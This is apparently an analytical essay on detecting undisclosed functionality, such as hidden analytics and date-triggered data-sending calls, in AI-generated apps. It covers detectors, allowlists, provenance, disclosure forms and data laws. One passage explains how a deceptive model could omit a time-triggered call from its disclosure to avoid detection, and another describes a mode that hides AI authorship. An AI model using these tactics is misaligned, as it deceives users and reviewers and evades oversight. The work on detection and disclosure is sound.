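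In one of the failed detections, the team had added seven lines to dnsmasq, a program that helps manage networks, so that it would run any command that arrived in a message with a certain option number. Claude Opus 4.6 found the function and saw that it ran commands, but decided it was probably dnsmasq's ordinary feature for running scripts and never checked where the commands came from. An analytics call is just as easy to explain away, because so many legitimate programs contain one.

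Claude Opus 4.6 and Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview share the highest success rate, 49%, on Quesma's benchmark leaderboard, *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?* Gemini also reported backdoors in 17% of the clean programs. GPT-5.2-Codex, at its highest effort setting, had a 46% success rate and no false alarms. Across all the models in the original test, the false-alarm rate was 28%. The benchmark has only 33 tasks. The leading models date from last winter, so 49% probably understates what the best current models can do.

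DAPLab, a research group at Columbia University, ran a harder test of reverse engineering that did not involve looking for backdoors. It used private programs to which experts had added defences against analysis. The best of five models scored 61.4% and fully solved 31.5% of the programs.

### How many alerts are right

Even a good detector produces mostly false alarms if what it looks for is rare. Suppose 1 change in 1,000 hides something, and a detector catches 90% of those changes but also flags 5% of the clean ones. In 100,000 changes:

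- 100 hide something, and the detector flags 90 of them.
- 99,900 are clean, and the detector flags 4,995 of them.

Only 90 of the 5,085 alerts are right, or about 1.8%. In general, if p is the share of changes that hide something, r the recall and f the false-alarm rate,

share of alerts that are right = p × r ÷ (p × r + (1 − p) × f).

This problem is hard to see in benchmarks because they contain a far larger share of bad examples than real life does. Guo and colleagues tested detectors of malicious packages on 6,420 malicious and 7,288 harmless npm packages, so nearly half were malicious. The last column below applies the formula to their results, assuming that 1 package in 1,000 is malicious.

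| Detector | How it works | Recall | False-alarm rate | Alerts that were right in the test | Alerts that would be right at 1 in 1,000 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Packj, static | Flags any use of sensitive functions | 98.7% | 86% | 50% | 0.1% |
| Packj, sandbox | Also runs the package | 95.5% | 64% | 57% | 0.1% |
| GuardDog | Searches for known patterns and follows data flows | 89.9% | 2.5% | 97% | 3.5% |
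| GENIE | Demands several kinds of system data flowing to one web address | 46.1% | 0.1% | 99.8% | 32% |
| SocketAI | An AI model judges the code alone | 44.4% | 0.7% | 98% | 6% |
| IntelGuard | An AI model compares the code with known malware | 93.8% | 1.5% | 98% | 6% |

In these conditions, 27 of every 28 GuardDog alerts would be wrong, even though its test results look almost perfect. GENIE misses more than half of the malicious packages, but its alerts would be by far the most trustworthy. The last column may be somewhat too pessimistic, because the harmless packages in the test were very popular, and such packages tend to cause more false alarms. But *Cutting the Gordian Knot* (2026) reports that the problem occurs in practice too, with existing tools raising more than 7,342 false alarms during a live scan of PyPI, the main Python package registry.

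Guo and colleagues attribute most of the differences between detectors to how they handle the fact that malicious and harmless packages use the same functions. A tool that flags code for what it can do will flag nearly everything, while one that requires proof of bad intent will miss a lot. IntelGuard and SocketAI used the same underlying model, GPT-4.1 mini, but IntelGuard's recall was 49 points higher, which the researchers attribute to its access to examples of known malware. This result is encouraging for detecting malware but less so for detecting telemetry, because telemetry code is often identical to something a reputable company publishes.

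The scores also depend on where the code runs. IntelGuard caught 98.5% of packages that sent out stolen data, but only 62.5% of those that tampered with web pages. All the tools were built mainly for server-side JavaScript, but the expense tracker runs in a browser.

Two good ways to make alerts more reliable are to act only when two different tools agree and to test fewer, more suspicious changes. If 1 in 1,000 packages is malicious, about 18% of the alerts on which GuardDog and IntelGuard agree would be right, although together they would catch 86% of the malicious packages instead of the 94% that IntelGuard catches alone. For the second approach, suppose the 90% detector from the first example examines only changes that add a new outside address, and 1 in 50 of those hides something. Then 27% of its alerts would be right, and a person could realistically check them all.

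### The expense tracker under all five methods

The table shows what each method would probably find in the tracker, assuming the analysis tools can read JavaScript and the traffic capture runs for an hour in December 2026.

| Method | Analytics call in the source | Dated call in the source | Chart library's usage report | Host's script |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Reading the diff | Visible | Visible, including the date | Only the line that loads the library | Absent from the repository |
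| Listing dependencies | Missed | Missed | Found, if somebody reads the documentation | Absent from the repository |
| Static analysis of capabilities | Network access reported, but the tracker needs that anyway | The same, whatever the date | Found, if the tool also examines the library | Absent from the repository |
| Static analysis of data flow | Found | Found | Probably missed, as it contains no expenses | Absent from the repository |
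| Traffic capture | Found | Missed | Found | Found only on the published app |
| Second AI model | Probably found | Probably found | Found only if the model opens the library's code | Absent from the repository |

Only the traffic capture can find the host's script. It is also the only method that misses the dated call because of when it is run. The combination that covers all four with the least work is therefore a careful reading of the source, by a person or a model, and a traffic capture of the published app. Finding out what the coding tool sends to its maker takes a separate capture on the developer's computer while the tool is working.

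Finding a call is also only part of the job. None of these methods can tell whether anybody told the user about it.

### Blocking without detecting

A network allowlist is a simple form of the confinement that Lampson described. It lists the addresses that a program may contact, and a firewall or sandbox blocks connections to all others. Recall and false alarm rates don't apply in the usual sense, although an incomplete list will break features that the user wants.

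If the list allows only the storage server, both unwanted calls in the tracker fail. The code discards the error from the analytics call, so the user wouldn't notice that failure, but the code doesn't catch the error from the dated call. From 1 March 2027, the tracker would store each expense and then report a failure, and some users would enter the expense again. Blocking can therefore accidentally expose hidden functionality by causing a puzzling bug.

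For code that runs in a browser, the website can send an allowlist along with the page. This is called a content security policy, and for the tracker it might be:

```
Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'self';
  connect-src https://storage.example; form-action 'self'
```

The first rule lets the browser load scripts, images and most other things only from the tracker's own address. It also blocks scripts written directly into the page. The second rule limits where scripts can send requests, and the third limits where forms can send data, which the first rule doesn't cover.

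This policy would block both unwanted calls and the chart library's usage report. It would also block a script loaded from the host's own domain, but the host delivers the policy along with the page, so it could add an exception for its script. A script on the app's own domain, like Lovable's, would be allowed to run. The policy would block that script's reports to the same domain, but many apps need to send requests to their own domain, and a policy that allowed those requests would also allow the reports.

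A policy like this also doesn't stop a script from sending the visitor to another website with expense data in the URL. It has no effect on code that runs on a server, which needs its own allowlist. As with any confinement, a program can still hide extra data in the messages it is allowed to send.

Both kinds of allowlist apply to the whole program, so the chart library can contact any address that the tracker can. *NodeShield* (2025) describes a way to limit each package separately in programs that run on Node.js, which is mostly used to run JavaScript on servers. It extends the list of a program's components to include what each one may do, such as use the network, read files or run code that it has put together itself, and enforces those limits while the program runs. A chart library without network permission couldn't report its usage, even if an update added code to do so. But network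 permission in NodeShield covers all network access, so a package that legitimately needs one address can contact any other. Combining NodeShield with an address allowlist would close most of that gap.

No list of addresses can separate a coding tool's telemetry from its features if both use the same addresses, as they do in Cursor.

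## Records and reviews that would reveal additions

Records from writing, building and publishing software could show how an unwanted call got into the code and whether anyone told the user. Most of these records exist for other reasons, such as finding every product that contains a library with a known flaw, so each covers only some of the places where an addition can be.

| Practice | Generated source | Libraries | Building and hosting | Coding tool |
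|---|---|---|---|---|
| List of components (SBOM) | Nothing | Their names, but not what they send | Nothing | Nothing |
| Signed provenance record | Which version of the source went in | Sometimes which versions went in | Files that somebody changed after the build | Nothing, unless its maker publishes a record for the tool |
| App-store privacy declaration | What the developer knows about | What the developer knows about | What the developer knows about | Nothing |
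| Log of the agent's session | Which files the agent edited | Install commands | Nothing | The agent's actions, but not the tool's reports to its maker |
| Commit label naming the AI tool | That AI helped | Nothing | Nothing | At most the tool's name |
| Requirement tracing | Additions of every kind | Additions, if somebody traces the libraries too | Code the compiler adds, at the strictest level | Nothing |

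### Lists of components and signed build records

For the tracker's chart library, the entry in a software bill of materials (SBOM) might read:

```
name:      chart-library
version:   4.2.0
supplier:  Example Charts
loads:     colour-scales 1.3.1, date-format 2.0.4
```

This would tell someone who used an app builder that the library exists, but not that it reports its usage.

CycloneDX, one of the two main SBOM formats, has an optional section for listing outside services, their addresses, and the kinds of data sent to them. But a program that makes an SBOM from the project's list of libraries can't fill in that section, because the addresses are in the code.

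A provenance record describes how a file was produced. The best-known scheme is SLSA (Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts). Its records contain a cryptographic hash that identifies the finished file, and they name the build service and normally the version of the source it used. Level 1 requires only that a record exist. At level 2, a hosted build service creates and signs the record, so a developer can't easily forge one on a laptop. At level 3, the service also keeps the signing key inaccessible to the build's own steps, so a malicious build script can't forge its own record.

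If somebody swaps the tracker's files after the build, their hashes no longer match the record. Comparing hashes would also reveal a script that the host inserts into a page, but browsers don't do this comparison and hardly any visitor would. The dated call in the tracker's source would pass at every level, because the record would correctly state that the file came from that source and the signature would be valid.

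Provenance records might be more useful for the coding tools themselves. xAI and Z.ai have published source code for their tools, and a signed record could show that the program people download was built from that code. The record would not stop the maker from switching a feature on remotely, as xAI could with Grok Build's uploads.

### What the developer declares

Apple and Google require developers to declare which kinds of data an app collects before it appears in their stores, including data that third-party libraries collect. Developers fill in the form themselves, so its accuracy depends on what they know about the app. Someone who built an app from a prompt may not know that it includes a chart library that collects data, and could answer every question honestly and still get the form wrong. Professional developers face a milder version of the problem, because some libraries' privacy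 policies omit data that the libraries collect.

Apple has partly addressed this with privacy manifests, files in which a library's maker states what the library collects. Apple's development software combines them into one report for the app's developer. It seems right for the library's maker to provide this information, because the maker is in the best position to know it. The manifests don't help with the expense tracker, which is a website and doesn't go through an app store.

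### Logs of what an agent did

Elastic, which sells software for searching logs, gave hundreds of its developers Cursor's coding agent and then realised that it had no record of what the agents did. Elastic's *13 million tool calls* describes the solution, a script that Cursor runs whenever the agent takes certain actions, such as running a command or reading or editing a file. The script recorded over 13 million events on more than 1,100 machines in about two months.

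Each entry gives the time, the user, the machine, the model, and the command or file involved. For the expense tracker, the log would show when the agent installed the chart library and when it edited the file that saves expenses. It would not show the analytics call, because Elastic chose not to record file contents, prompts or the model's replies.

If someone found a call another way, the log would still help explain it, because it lists the files the agent read beforehand. If one of those files was a skill from an unknown publisher, an investigator would know to examine that skill next.

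Elastic's script receives only the events that Cursor exposes. If the tool itself uploads data, as ZCode did with archives, the upload would probably leave no entry because it isn't an action by the agent. Developers with administrator rights can also remove the script, though Elastic points out that a busy machine with no events is itself suspicious.

A log like this is telemetry about employees. Before switching it on everywhere, Elastic published an internal page explaining what the log collected, who could read it and why. The company reports no objections to the basic idea, although employees may not feel free to object.

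### Labels that name the AI tool

Some projects ask contributors to add a line such as "Assisted-by: LLM" to the description of a commit, or to mention AI in the pull request. Reviewers can use these labels to decide which changes to read more carefully, although a label doesn't show what the AI added. If the label names the model, people can also find that model's work later, which would be useful if somebody discovered that the model had a backdoor.

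Few contributions disclose AI use. *Perspective on AI and quantum open-source software* (2026) compares 11 quantum-computing projects with eight other scientific Python projects. In the median quantum project, 0.43% of the pull requests from 2026 disclosed AI use. The median for the other group was 4.56%, even though all eight projects ask for disclosure. Averages can also be misleading. In one project, half of the commits disclosed AI use, but a single maintainer wrote 1,107 of those 1,145.

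These figures are minimums for AI use. *Comprehension Audits to Mitigate Risks from Automated AI Research* (2026) explains that suggestions accepted inside a code editor leave no trace, and that squashing several commits into one can erase their labels. A tool's defaults probably also affect whether commits credit AI. *The AI Attribution Paradox* (2025) reports that, in a sample of commits that nearly all mentioned AI, the choice of tool was the best predictor of whether a commit explicitly credited AI with the work.

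Some projects prohibit AI labels in their commit history. *What Open-Source Projects Tell Their Coding Agents* (2026) is a census of the instruction files that projects write for agents. Among those with rules on commit messages, 7.4% prohibit naming the AI and 3.5% require it. For pull requests, more require disclosure (5.8%) than prohibit it (1.9%). Kubernetes, a large project for managing servers, requires contributors to disclose AI help but forbids "assisted-by" lines, according to LWN.net as quoted in a message to the Linux kernel's mailing list.

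The Linux kernel project, which develops the core of the Linux operating system, tried permanent labels for part of 2026. At first the label had to name the tool and the model version. In July, Brauner (2026), in *[PATCH] coding-assistants*, shortened it to "Assisted-by: LLM", arguing that the names were free advertising for software companies and gave maintainers little information. The change also made it impossible to search for one model's work.

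By October the kernel's maintainers had decided to drop the label. Linuxiac's *Linus Torvalds Rejects AI Coding Bans as Linux Rethinks Disclosure Rules* (2026) gives the figures behind the proposal. About 10% of the 18,533 commits in the coming version had the label, though developers believed AI use was much more common. Some contributors didn't know about the rule and others deliberately ignored it. One developer had argued in a reply to the July proposal that nobody could enforce the rule, so it penalised honest contributors. But a maintainer wrote in a later thread that the label helped them decide how to review a patch.

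The Linux kernel documentation's *AI Coding Assistants* no longer has a section on labels, but a human must still review all AI-generated code and take responsibility for it. *Kernel Guidelines for Tool-Generated Content* also still asks contributors to disclose which tools they used, what prompts they gave, which parts the tool affected and how they tested the result, so the headline of Slashdot's *Linux Maintainers Can Now Submit AI-Generated Code Without Declaring It* (2026) goes slightly too far. Contributors can put these details in the cover letter, a message that accompanies a set of patches but doesn't become part of the code's history. That gives reviewers what they need, but someone auditing the code five years later would have to search the mailing list.

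Losing the label matters little for finding hidden functionality. If AI helps with most changes, a label that says only "LLM" barely narrows the search.

### A setting that removes the label

In March 2026 Anthropic accidentally leaked the source code of Claude Code, as Nolan reported in *Anthropic mistakenly leaks its own AI coding tool’s source code* (2026). One file in *source dump of claude code*, a public copy of the leak, contains an "undercover mode" for contributions to public projects. The mode removes all attribution and instructs the model not to include "any mention that you are an AI" and to write commit messages as a human developer would.

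In the version that Anthropic's employees use, the mode switches on automatically unless the project is on a list of internal projects, and employees can't force it off. In the customer version, the code does nothing.

According to the file's comments, the mode is meant to prevent leaks of unreleased models' codenames and other internal information. That is a real concern, and not only for Anthropic. In the kernel discussion, Chehab (2026) quotes the developer Theodore Ts'o as saying that some contributors use unreleased products whose names aren't public. But Ts'o's solution was to leave out the version. The label "Assisted-by: LLM" would disclose the use of AI without revealing any codename, so Anthropic's stated reason doesn't justify hiding the AI altogether.

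Employees see a notice the first time the mode turns on automatically, but the maintainers who receive the code are not told about it. The file contains no instruction for the model to add unrequested behaviour to their projects.

### How carefully people read generated code

Somebody has to read a change whether or not it has a label. *From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026) surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents. Of these, 56% said they inspected diffs and 63% said they compared the output with the requirements. But 69% agreed that reading line by line couldn't keep up with the amount of code agents produce.

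*Why Johnny Can't Vibe* (2026) surveyed 116 people, and only 25.0% said they thoroughly read every line of AI-generated code before running it. The most common check, reported by 73.3%, was to run the code and look at the output. The tracker would pass that check with both unwanted calls in place, because expenses would save and the chart would appear. The survey figures are self-reported, so the real ones may well be lower.

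People who build software mainly by prompting seem to check less. *Vibe Coding in Practice* (2025), a review of practitioners' accounts, classified 132 descriptions of how people checked such code. In 36% they skipped checking, and in another 18% they trusted the result. Interviews in *From Preventive to Reactive* (2026) suggest that developers are also more lenient with internal or experimental projects than with code they will release. They would be lenient with an expense tracker for their own family, even though it contains more private information than many commercial products.

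To find additions, a reviewer has to start from the code and ask which request each part serves. Comparing the output with the requirements usually means checking that each request works, which misses additions because they aren't among the requests.

### Tracing code back to a request

DO-178C, the standard that regulators accept for software on civil aircraft, sorts software into five levels by how bad a failure would be. At the three strictest levels, developers must trace the code to detailed requirements, and those requirements to broader ones, in both directions. Tracing from requirements to code reveals anything missing, while tracing from code back to requirements reveals anything that is there without a reason.

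Suppose the user asked for the expense tracker in three lines:

1. Let me enter expenses with a date, an amount and a category.
2. Save them to my account.
3. Show a monthly chart by category.

Tracing the code backwards would give something like this:

| Part of the code | Requirement | What happens to it |
|---|---|---|
| Entry form | Line 1 | It stays |
| Call that stores an expense | Line 2 | It stays |
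| Chart library | Line 3 | The chart stays, but the usage report needs an explanation |
| Rejecting 31 February | None directly | Somebody writes a new requirement, "dates must exist" |
| Login check | None directly | Somebody writes a new requirement, "only I can see my account" |
| Error log | None | The user decides |
| Call to the analytics company | None | Somebody explains it or removes it |
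| Dated call to another server | None | Somebody explains it or removes it |

DO-178C calls requirements like "dates must exist" derived requirements. They come from the developers' design decisions, not the customer, and the developers must pass them to the people who assess the safety of the whole system. A prompt leaves most of a program's needs unstated, and this process handles that by allowing useful additions only after somebody has written them down and somebody else has reviewed them.

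As a second check, the standard requires developers to base their tests on the requirements and measure which parts of the code those tests run. If a part never ran, they have to find out why. A test or a requirement may be missing. The code may be there for a different configuration, in which case they must show that it can't run by accident. If the code has no purpose, they remove it.

This check would catch the tracker's dated call. Tests of the three lines in January 2027 would never run that part of the code, so the coverage report would point to it even if the tester didn't suspect that the date mattered. A trigger that a million random tests would miss therefore makes the code behind it easier to find, because the report shows that code as unused. The analytics call runs on every save, so it would look normal in the coverage report, and only the tracing would reveal it. Neither check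 would reveal much about code that fetches its instructions from a server and always runs.

At the strictest level, developers must also account for machine instructions that the compiler adds and that can't be traced to the source code. This rule would have required developers to explain the telemetry call that Microsoft's compiler inserted.

All of this takes a lot of work, especially when the request is casual. Suppose the tracker has 60 functions, of which 15 trace directly to the three lines. The other 45 need derived requirements. If the user spends half a minute on each, that takes over 22 minutes for an app they described in one minute. The libraries contain far more code than the tracker and would need the same treatment.

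Having the model write the requirements too would save time, but the user, or at least somebody other than the model, has to approve the derived requirements. Otherwise, a model that added an analytics call could just as easily add the requirement "the app shall report usage to the analytics company", and all the code would trace to a requirement.

A version that takes less work would trace only the behaviour most likely to matter to the user, such as sending data out of the app. The tracker has four such behaviours, including the chart library's report, and most people could judge them in a minute or two.

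### A one-page disclosure

A coding agent could provide that shorter list itself. For the tracker, a complete one might look like this:

```
EXPENSE TRACKER: DISCLOSURE

1. Where the app sends data
   NOT REQUESTED  stats.example    a copy of each expense, on every save
   NOT REQUESTED  other.example    all expenses, on every save
                                   from 1 March 2027
   Requested      storage.example  each expense, on every save

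2. Libraries that report by default
   chart-library 4.2.0   its version and the browser type, to
                         charts.example, when it first loads
                         To stop this: usageReport = false

3. Other additions
   Login check; rejection of impossible dates;
   error log, kept in the user's account

4. Not covered
   Scripts the host adds; data the coding tool sends its maker
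```

The kernel's guidelines are a useful precedent, but they cover how a contributor made the code, whereas this form describes what the code does. The form lists unrequested destinations first so that readers don't miss them, as they could easily miss Sears's notice, which was accurate but appeared on the 75th line. Having to write "NOT REQUESTED" next to an address might also lead an agent to leave the network call out of the code, although nobody seems to have tested this.

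Agents already write descriptions of their work, and many projects give them rules for doing so. Of the instruction files in the census that had rules on pull-request descriptions, 27.2% required evidence of testing. Filling in four more headings would be little extra work. It would be safer for the coding tool to require the form than for each user to ask for it, because agents often ignored written instructions about logging in Ouatiti and colleagues' study.

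The form may be unreliable because the model would fill it in. In Privacy International's projects, the AI described unfinished work as complete and gave inaccurate accounts of its changes. *Analyzing Message-Code Inconsistency in AI Coding Agent-Authored Pull Requests* (2026) warns that agents write descriptions without human oversight and could produce misleading explanations on a large scale. If a model had a hidden aim, leaving the relevant addition off the form would serve that aim.

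A list of addresses is easy to check, unlike a general assurance that the code is safe. A reviewer can compare the destinations on the list with those in a traffic capture.

- C − L contains destinations that the app contacted and the form left out. If it isn't empty, the form is wrong.
- L − C contains destinations on the form that the capture didn't record. Either the test missed something or the form lists a call that doesn't exist.

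A capture of the tracker in December 2026 would record every address on the form except other.example, so L − C would contain that address. The form gives the date, so the tester would know to set the clock forward. An honest disclosure therefore makes the capture more effective. If the form had left out stats.example, C − L would contain it. A computer can make both comparisons, but without a list somebody has to judge every address from scratch.

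Reviewers can also check the form's descriptions against the capture. If the form lists "anonymous usage statistics" but the capture contains an expense for zebra food, that description is false.

A deceptive model would do best to omit only the dated call from the form. Then neither the form nor the December capture would include other.example, and comparing them would show no discrepancy. Traffic can therefore expose a false list only when the undisclosed behaviour happens during the test. The gap gets much smaller if the user also turns the approved part of the list into an allowlist, which blocks any address the model left out.

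Honest mistakes are easier to deal with. The coding tool could fill in most of the first two headings by analysing the code and looking up each library's defaults, and the model would explain what each destination is for. If the model's account differed from the analysis, the tool could show the user both.

The model can't complete the fourth heading without other people's help, because it can't predict what a host will add next month. Hosts could publish the same kind of list for their scripts, and makers of coding tools could publish one for their own reports. Neither a capture nor an allowlist can show whether storage.example passes the expense data on to another company.

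## Laws on disclosing data collection and undeclared functions

No law seems to require a coding agent to list the addresses its code contacts, but several laws require someone to disclose some of that information. In the EU, reading data from a visitor's device, handling personal data or putting a product on the market can create a duty to disclose. US federal law mostly prohibits misleading claims and omissions. Russia has a certification category for undocumented functions, and China requires products that collect user data to disclose this.

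### EU rules on devices and personal data

Article 5(3) of the EU's ePrivacy Directive is the reason websites have cookie banners. As quoted in Hunton's *EDPB publishes guidelines to clarify scope of EU cookie notice*, it requires anyone who stores information on a user's device, or accesses information already there, to get the user's consent, based on "clear and comprehensive information". It exempts what is needed solely to transmit a communication and what is strictly necessary to provide a service the user explicitly requested.

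The second exception resembles N in the definition of hidden functionality, but it depends on what the visitor requested, not what whoever commissioned the app requested. A visitor who saves an expense has asked the app to send it to the storage server, but not to send a copy to an analytics company.

The European Data Protection Board, which brings together the EU's national privacy regulators, reads the rule broadly. Its final guidelines, EDPB (2024), say the rule covers "similar technologies" as well as cookies. They treat JavaScript that tells a browser to send information back as a form of access, so the tracker's analytics call would need consent even though it sets no cookie. The rule also covers information that isn't personal, so the chart library's report of the browser type probably needs consent too. The guidelines do not bind the courts. Mondaq's *EDPB reiterates its broad reading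 of the cookie rule* warns that this reading may have unintended consequences.

The General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) applies once the information relates to an identifiable person, as expenses linked to an account do. It places most duties on the "controller", whoever decides why and how to process the data. Article 13 requires the controller, when it collects people's data, to tell them its identity, what the data is for, how long it will keep the data and who will receive it. The controller may describe the recipients by category, such as "analytics providers". But if someone later asks what happened to their own data, the controller must normally name the actual recipients, as the EU's Court of Justice decided in *Österreichische Post* (2023). An owner who doesn't know about the analytics company can't give its category or its name.

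In November 2025 the European Commission proposed moving the device rule for personal data into the GDPR and dropping the consent requirement for some purposes, including audience statistics that a website compiles solely for its own use. This exemption would help an owner who relies on analytics like Lovable's, but would be little help to one whose app reports to an unknown company.

### EU rules on products

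The European Union's Cyber Resilience Act sets security requirements for software and connected devices that businesses supply in the EU. One requirement, which comes close to banning unrequested data collection, is that a product may process only data "limited to what is necessary in relation to the intended purpose". This applies to data that is "personal or other", so it covers a library's version number as well as a person's name.

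The manufacturer defines the intended purpose in its own instructions, advertising and technical documents, which weakens the rule. A company that wants analytics can add "and to help us improve the product" to the purpose, just as a model could invent a requirement to justify its own code. The rule is more useful against additions that the manufacturer doesn't know about, because nobody will have written a purpose for them.

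The Act requires less disclosure. Manufacturers must draw up an SBOM that covers at least the libraries the product loads directly, but they can decide whether to show it to users. They must supply each product with information that includes its purpose, how long security support will last and how to delete user data, but they do not have to list the addresses the product contacts.

Most of the Act does not apply yet. According to the timeline in the European Commission's *Cyber Resilience Act*, the reporting duties start on 11 September 2026 and the whole Act applies from 11 December 2027. A manufacturer must now send the authorities an early warning within 24 hours of learning about a severe incident, and a fuller notice within 72 hours. An incident can count as severe if it puts malicious code into a product, so a company that found the dated call in its app, and had reason to think an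 attacker had planted it, would probably have to report it. It is less clear whether a company would have to report an ordinary analytics call. Small companies must also meet the 24-hour deadline, but authorities cannot fine them for missing it.

The Commission published guidance on the Act on 27 July 2026, which Digital Policy Alert's *European Commission adopted Guidance on implementation of Cyber Resilience Act* describes as non-binding. According to passages quoted by Lewis Silkin, a website is not in itself a product under the Act, even though some of its code runs on the visitor's device. The Act would generally not apply to the expense tracker if a business offered it as a web page, but would apply if the business offered it as a phone app. This distinction is awkward for AI-generated apps because many app builders mainly produce websites, and an analytics call does the same thing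 on a website and in a phone app.

The new Product Liability Directive covers more kinds of software. Pliauskaite (2024), in *EU Product Liability Directive Reform*, lists stand-alone software, software as a service and AI systems. Someone harmed by a defective product can claim compensation from its manufacturer without proving that the manufacturer was careless. According to the summary in the European Parliament's *Liability for defective products*, the directive applies to products placed on the market after 9 December 2026, which is also the deadline for EU countries to put it into national law.

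The directive will do little about telemetry, however, because it covers only injury, damage to property, and the destruction or corruption of data that people don't use for work. According to its introductory text, an invasion of privacy is not enough by itself. A family might have a claim if hidden code deleted their expense records, but if it sent the records to a stranger, they would have to rely on the GDPR, which allows compensation for non-financial harm but requires a breach of its own rules.

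### The Sears case and deceptive practices in the US

The FTC can act against "unfair or deceptive" business practices, and in 2009 it used that power against Sears over software that collected data. Sears's licence agreement described the tracking accurately, but the agency argued that people would have wanted to know its extent before they installed the software.

According to the FTC's summary, the final order required Sears to destroy the data it had collected. If Sears offered tracking software again, it had to state clearly and prominently what types of data the software would monitor, record or transmit, and whether a third party would use any of it. This disclosure had to appear before installation and separately from any licence agreement. These terms are a good practical version of D, the set of behaviours disclosed where a user would reasonably look.

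An FTC order binds only the company it names, but the agency clearly meant others to take notice, since its advice to businesses, *Someone to Watch Over Me?*, draws lessons for retailers from the case.

The agency later loosened the order at the company's request, as PogoWasRight's *FTC Approves Sears Holdings Management Corporation Petition* records. The revised definition of a tracking application excludes software that reports only on its own settings, operation and use. That exception would cover the chart library's usage report but probably not the analytics call, which copies the contents of each expense.

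The FTC has since taken more interest in AI companies. CBS News reported in *FTC issues subpoenas to Anthropic and OpenAI over safety incidents* (2026) that the agency was investigating possible consumer protection violations and had reportedly sought documents on safety incidents, safeguards and privacy policies.

### Russia's tests for undeclared capabilities

A 1999 guidance document from Russia's State Technical Commission defines "undeclared capabilities" as functions that a program's documentation leaves out or describes incorrectly, and that could compromise the confidentiality, availability or integrity of the information the program handles. The definition applies whether or not anyone added the function on purpose, but the document calls a function a "program implant" if someone inserted it deliberately to run under certain conditions.

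This is narrower than hidden functionality in one respect, because the function has to be capable of harm. A concealed game would not count unless it created a security risk. It is also easier to apply, because the examiner compares the program with its documentation rather than working out what a user wanted. A documented analytics call would pass, even if nobody had asked for it.

The document sets four levels of testing based on how secret the protected information is. Each level includes the tests from the levels below it.

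| Level | Information the software protects | Main tests added |
|---|---|---|
| 4 | Confidential | Record a checksum for every file, look for missing or superfluous files, and check that the source matches the executable |
| 3 | Secret | Look for superfluous procedures, map how procedures call each other and share data, then run them and compare the paths they take with the map |
| 2 | Top secret | Compare paths down to individual branches, search for dangerous code patterns, and compare how functions work with their description |
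| 1 | Of special importance | Check the source against the executable with certified compilers, and search for dangerous patterns by meaning as well as form |

The tracker's two unwanted calls would pass the file checks at level 4 because they are in a file that belongs there. Level 3 would map the function that contains them, so a careful examiner might notice where its data goes. At level 2, the tests should expose the dated call even in January 2027, because its branch would appear on the map but not in the test runs. The comparison with the written description should expose the analytics call. Level 1 responds to the problem Thompson described, though it requires trusting whoever certified the compiler.

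FSTEC, the agency that now certifies security products in Russia, set out the current certification scheme in Order No. 76, which has been in force since 1 January 2021. The scheme has six levels of trust, and tests for undeclared capabilities begin at Level 6, the lowest. Level 4 adds a search for covert channels that use memory, including an estimate of how much data each could carry. The manufacturer does the tests first, and then an independent laboratory repeats them for certification. Шевцов, an FSTEC official, presented a testing method that combines a study of the documents with static, dynamic and manual analysis.

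From level 5, the developer has to supply source code, except for third-party components that have no effect on the product's security functions. If information about a third-party component is missing, the developer has to either design protections that block anything dangerous it might do or reverse-engineer it to find out what it does. For the tracker's chart library, blocking network access would be much less work than reverse-engineering it.

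These rules apply to security products and other protected systems, such as those that handle state secrets, government data or critical infrastructure. An ordinary business app does not need a certificate, and few small companies could afford one. The scheme shows that a government can require, as a condition of approval, that a program do nothing its documentation omits, at least where the government can require source code and pay for laboratories. The rules don't show whether the laboratories actually find most undeclared capabilities.

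### China's duty to announce data collection

China's Cybersecurity Law has the most direct wording. If a network product or service can collect user information, its provider "shall clearly inform users and obtain their consent", in CSET's translation, *Cybersecurity Law of the People's Republic of China* (2026). Additional rules apply to personal information, which implies that the basic duty also covers non-personal information. Amendments in force since 1 January 2026 moved this duty from Article 22 to Article 24. The Library of Congress' *China* (2026) notes that the amendments also raised fines and extended the law's reach outside the country.

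The sentence makes no exception for a provider who didn't know about the collection or considers it harmless. Under this wording, Z.ai's background uploads from ZCode look like a breach, at least for users in China, because the company had told users only about code they sent in conversation.

The law refers breaches of the notice duty to other legislation for punishment, and only if they infringe people's rights over personal information. A provider that failed to disclose a harmless usage count would therefore break the rule but face no obvious penalty. A provider that installs a "malicious program" is usually fined 50,000 to 500,000 yuan if it refuses to correct the problem or causes harm, and the fine can reach 10 million yuan (about $1.5 million) if the consequences are exceptionally severe. An undisclosed analytics call would fall under this heavier rule only if the authorities considered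 it malicious.

### A bookkeeper's app and an unknown analytics company

Suppose a bookkeeper in Dublin uses an app builder to make the expense tracker and publishes it as a website for clients. The AI-written code sends each expense and the client's account name to an analytics company the bookkeeper has never heard of.

The clients know only the bookkeeper, and EU law most likely makes the bookkeeper responsible for telling them about the analytics. That duty falls on the controller, who decides why and how to process data, but the bookkeeper made no decisions about the analytics. Two judgments of the Court of Justice suggest that the bookkeeper could still be a controller, though neither involved AI.

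In *Fashion ID* (2019), a German clothes shop put Facebook's "Like" button on its website. The button sent visitors' data to Facebook whether or not they clicked it. The court held that the shop shared responsibility for collecting and sending the data and had to inform visitors about its part, but was not responsible for what Facebook did with the data afterwards. The court observed, however, that the shop knew what the button did.

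*Nacionalinis visuomenės sveikatos centras* (2023) is closer to the bookkeeper's case. A Lithuanian public health agency had asked a company to develop a Covid-19 app, which became available to the public although the agency never acquired it. The court held that someone who commissions an app and helps decide its purposes can be a controller without having agreed to the specific processing, unless they expressly objected before the release. The bookkeeper commissioned an app, never objected and, unlike the agency, published it. But the agency had helped shape what data its app collected, while the bookkeeper did not mention analytics in the prompt.

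A court would probably still treat the bookkeeper as a controller. Otherwise, a business could avoid its duties by not looking at its own code, and visitors would not know whom to ask. Under the same 2023 judgment, however, a regulator may impose a GDPR fine only for an intentional or negligent breach. Publishing generated code without checking where it sends data is arguably negligent, since an hour's traffic capture would have revealed this call. But most small business owners have never heard of a traffic capture, and no court seems to have decided what checks they must make.

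In the US, the result would depend more on what the bookkeeper had said. If the app's privacy page included the promise "we never share your data", that promise would be false, and the FTC does not have to prove that a business intended to deceive. If the app had no privacy page, the agency would have to argue that silence misled people or that the practice was unfair, which is harder.

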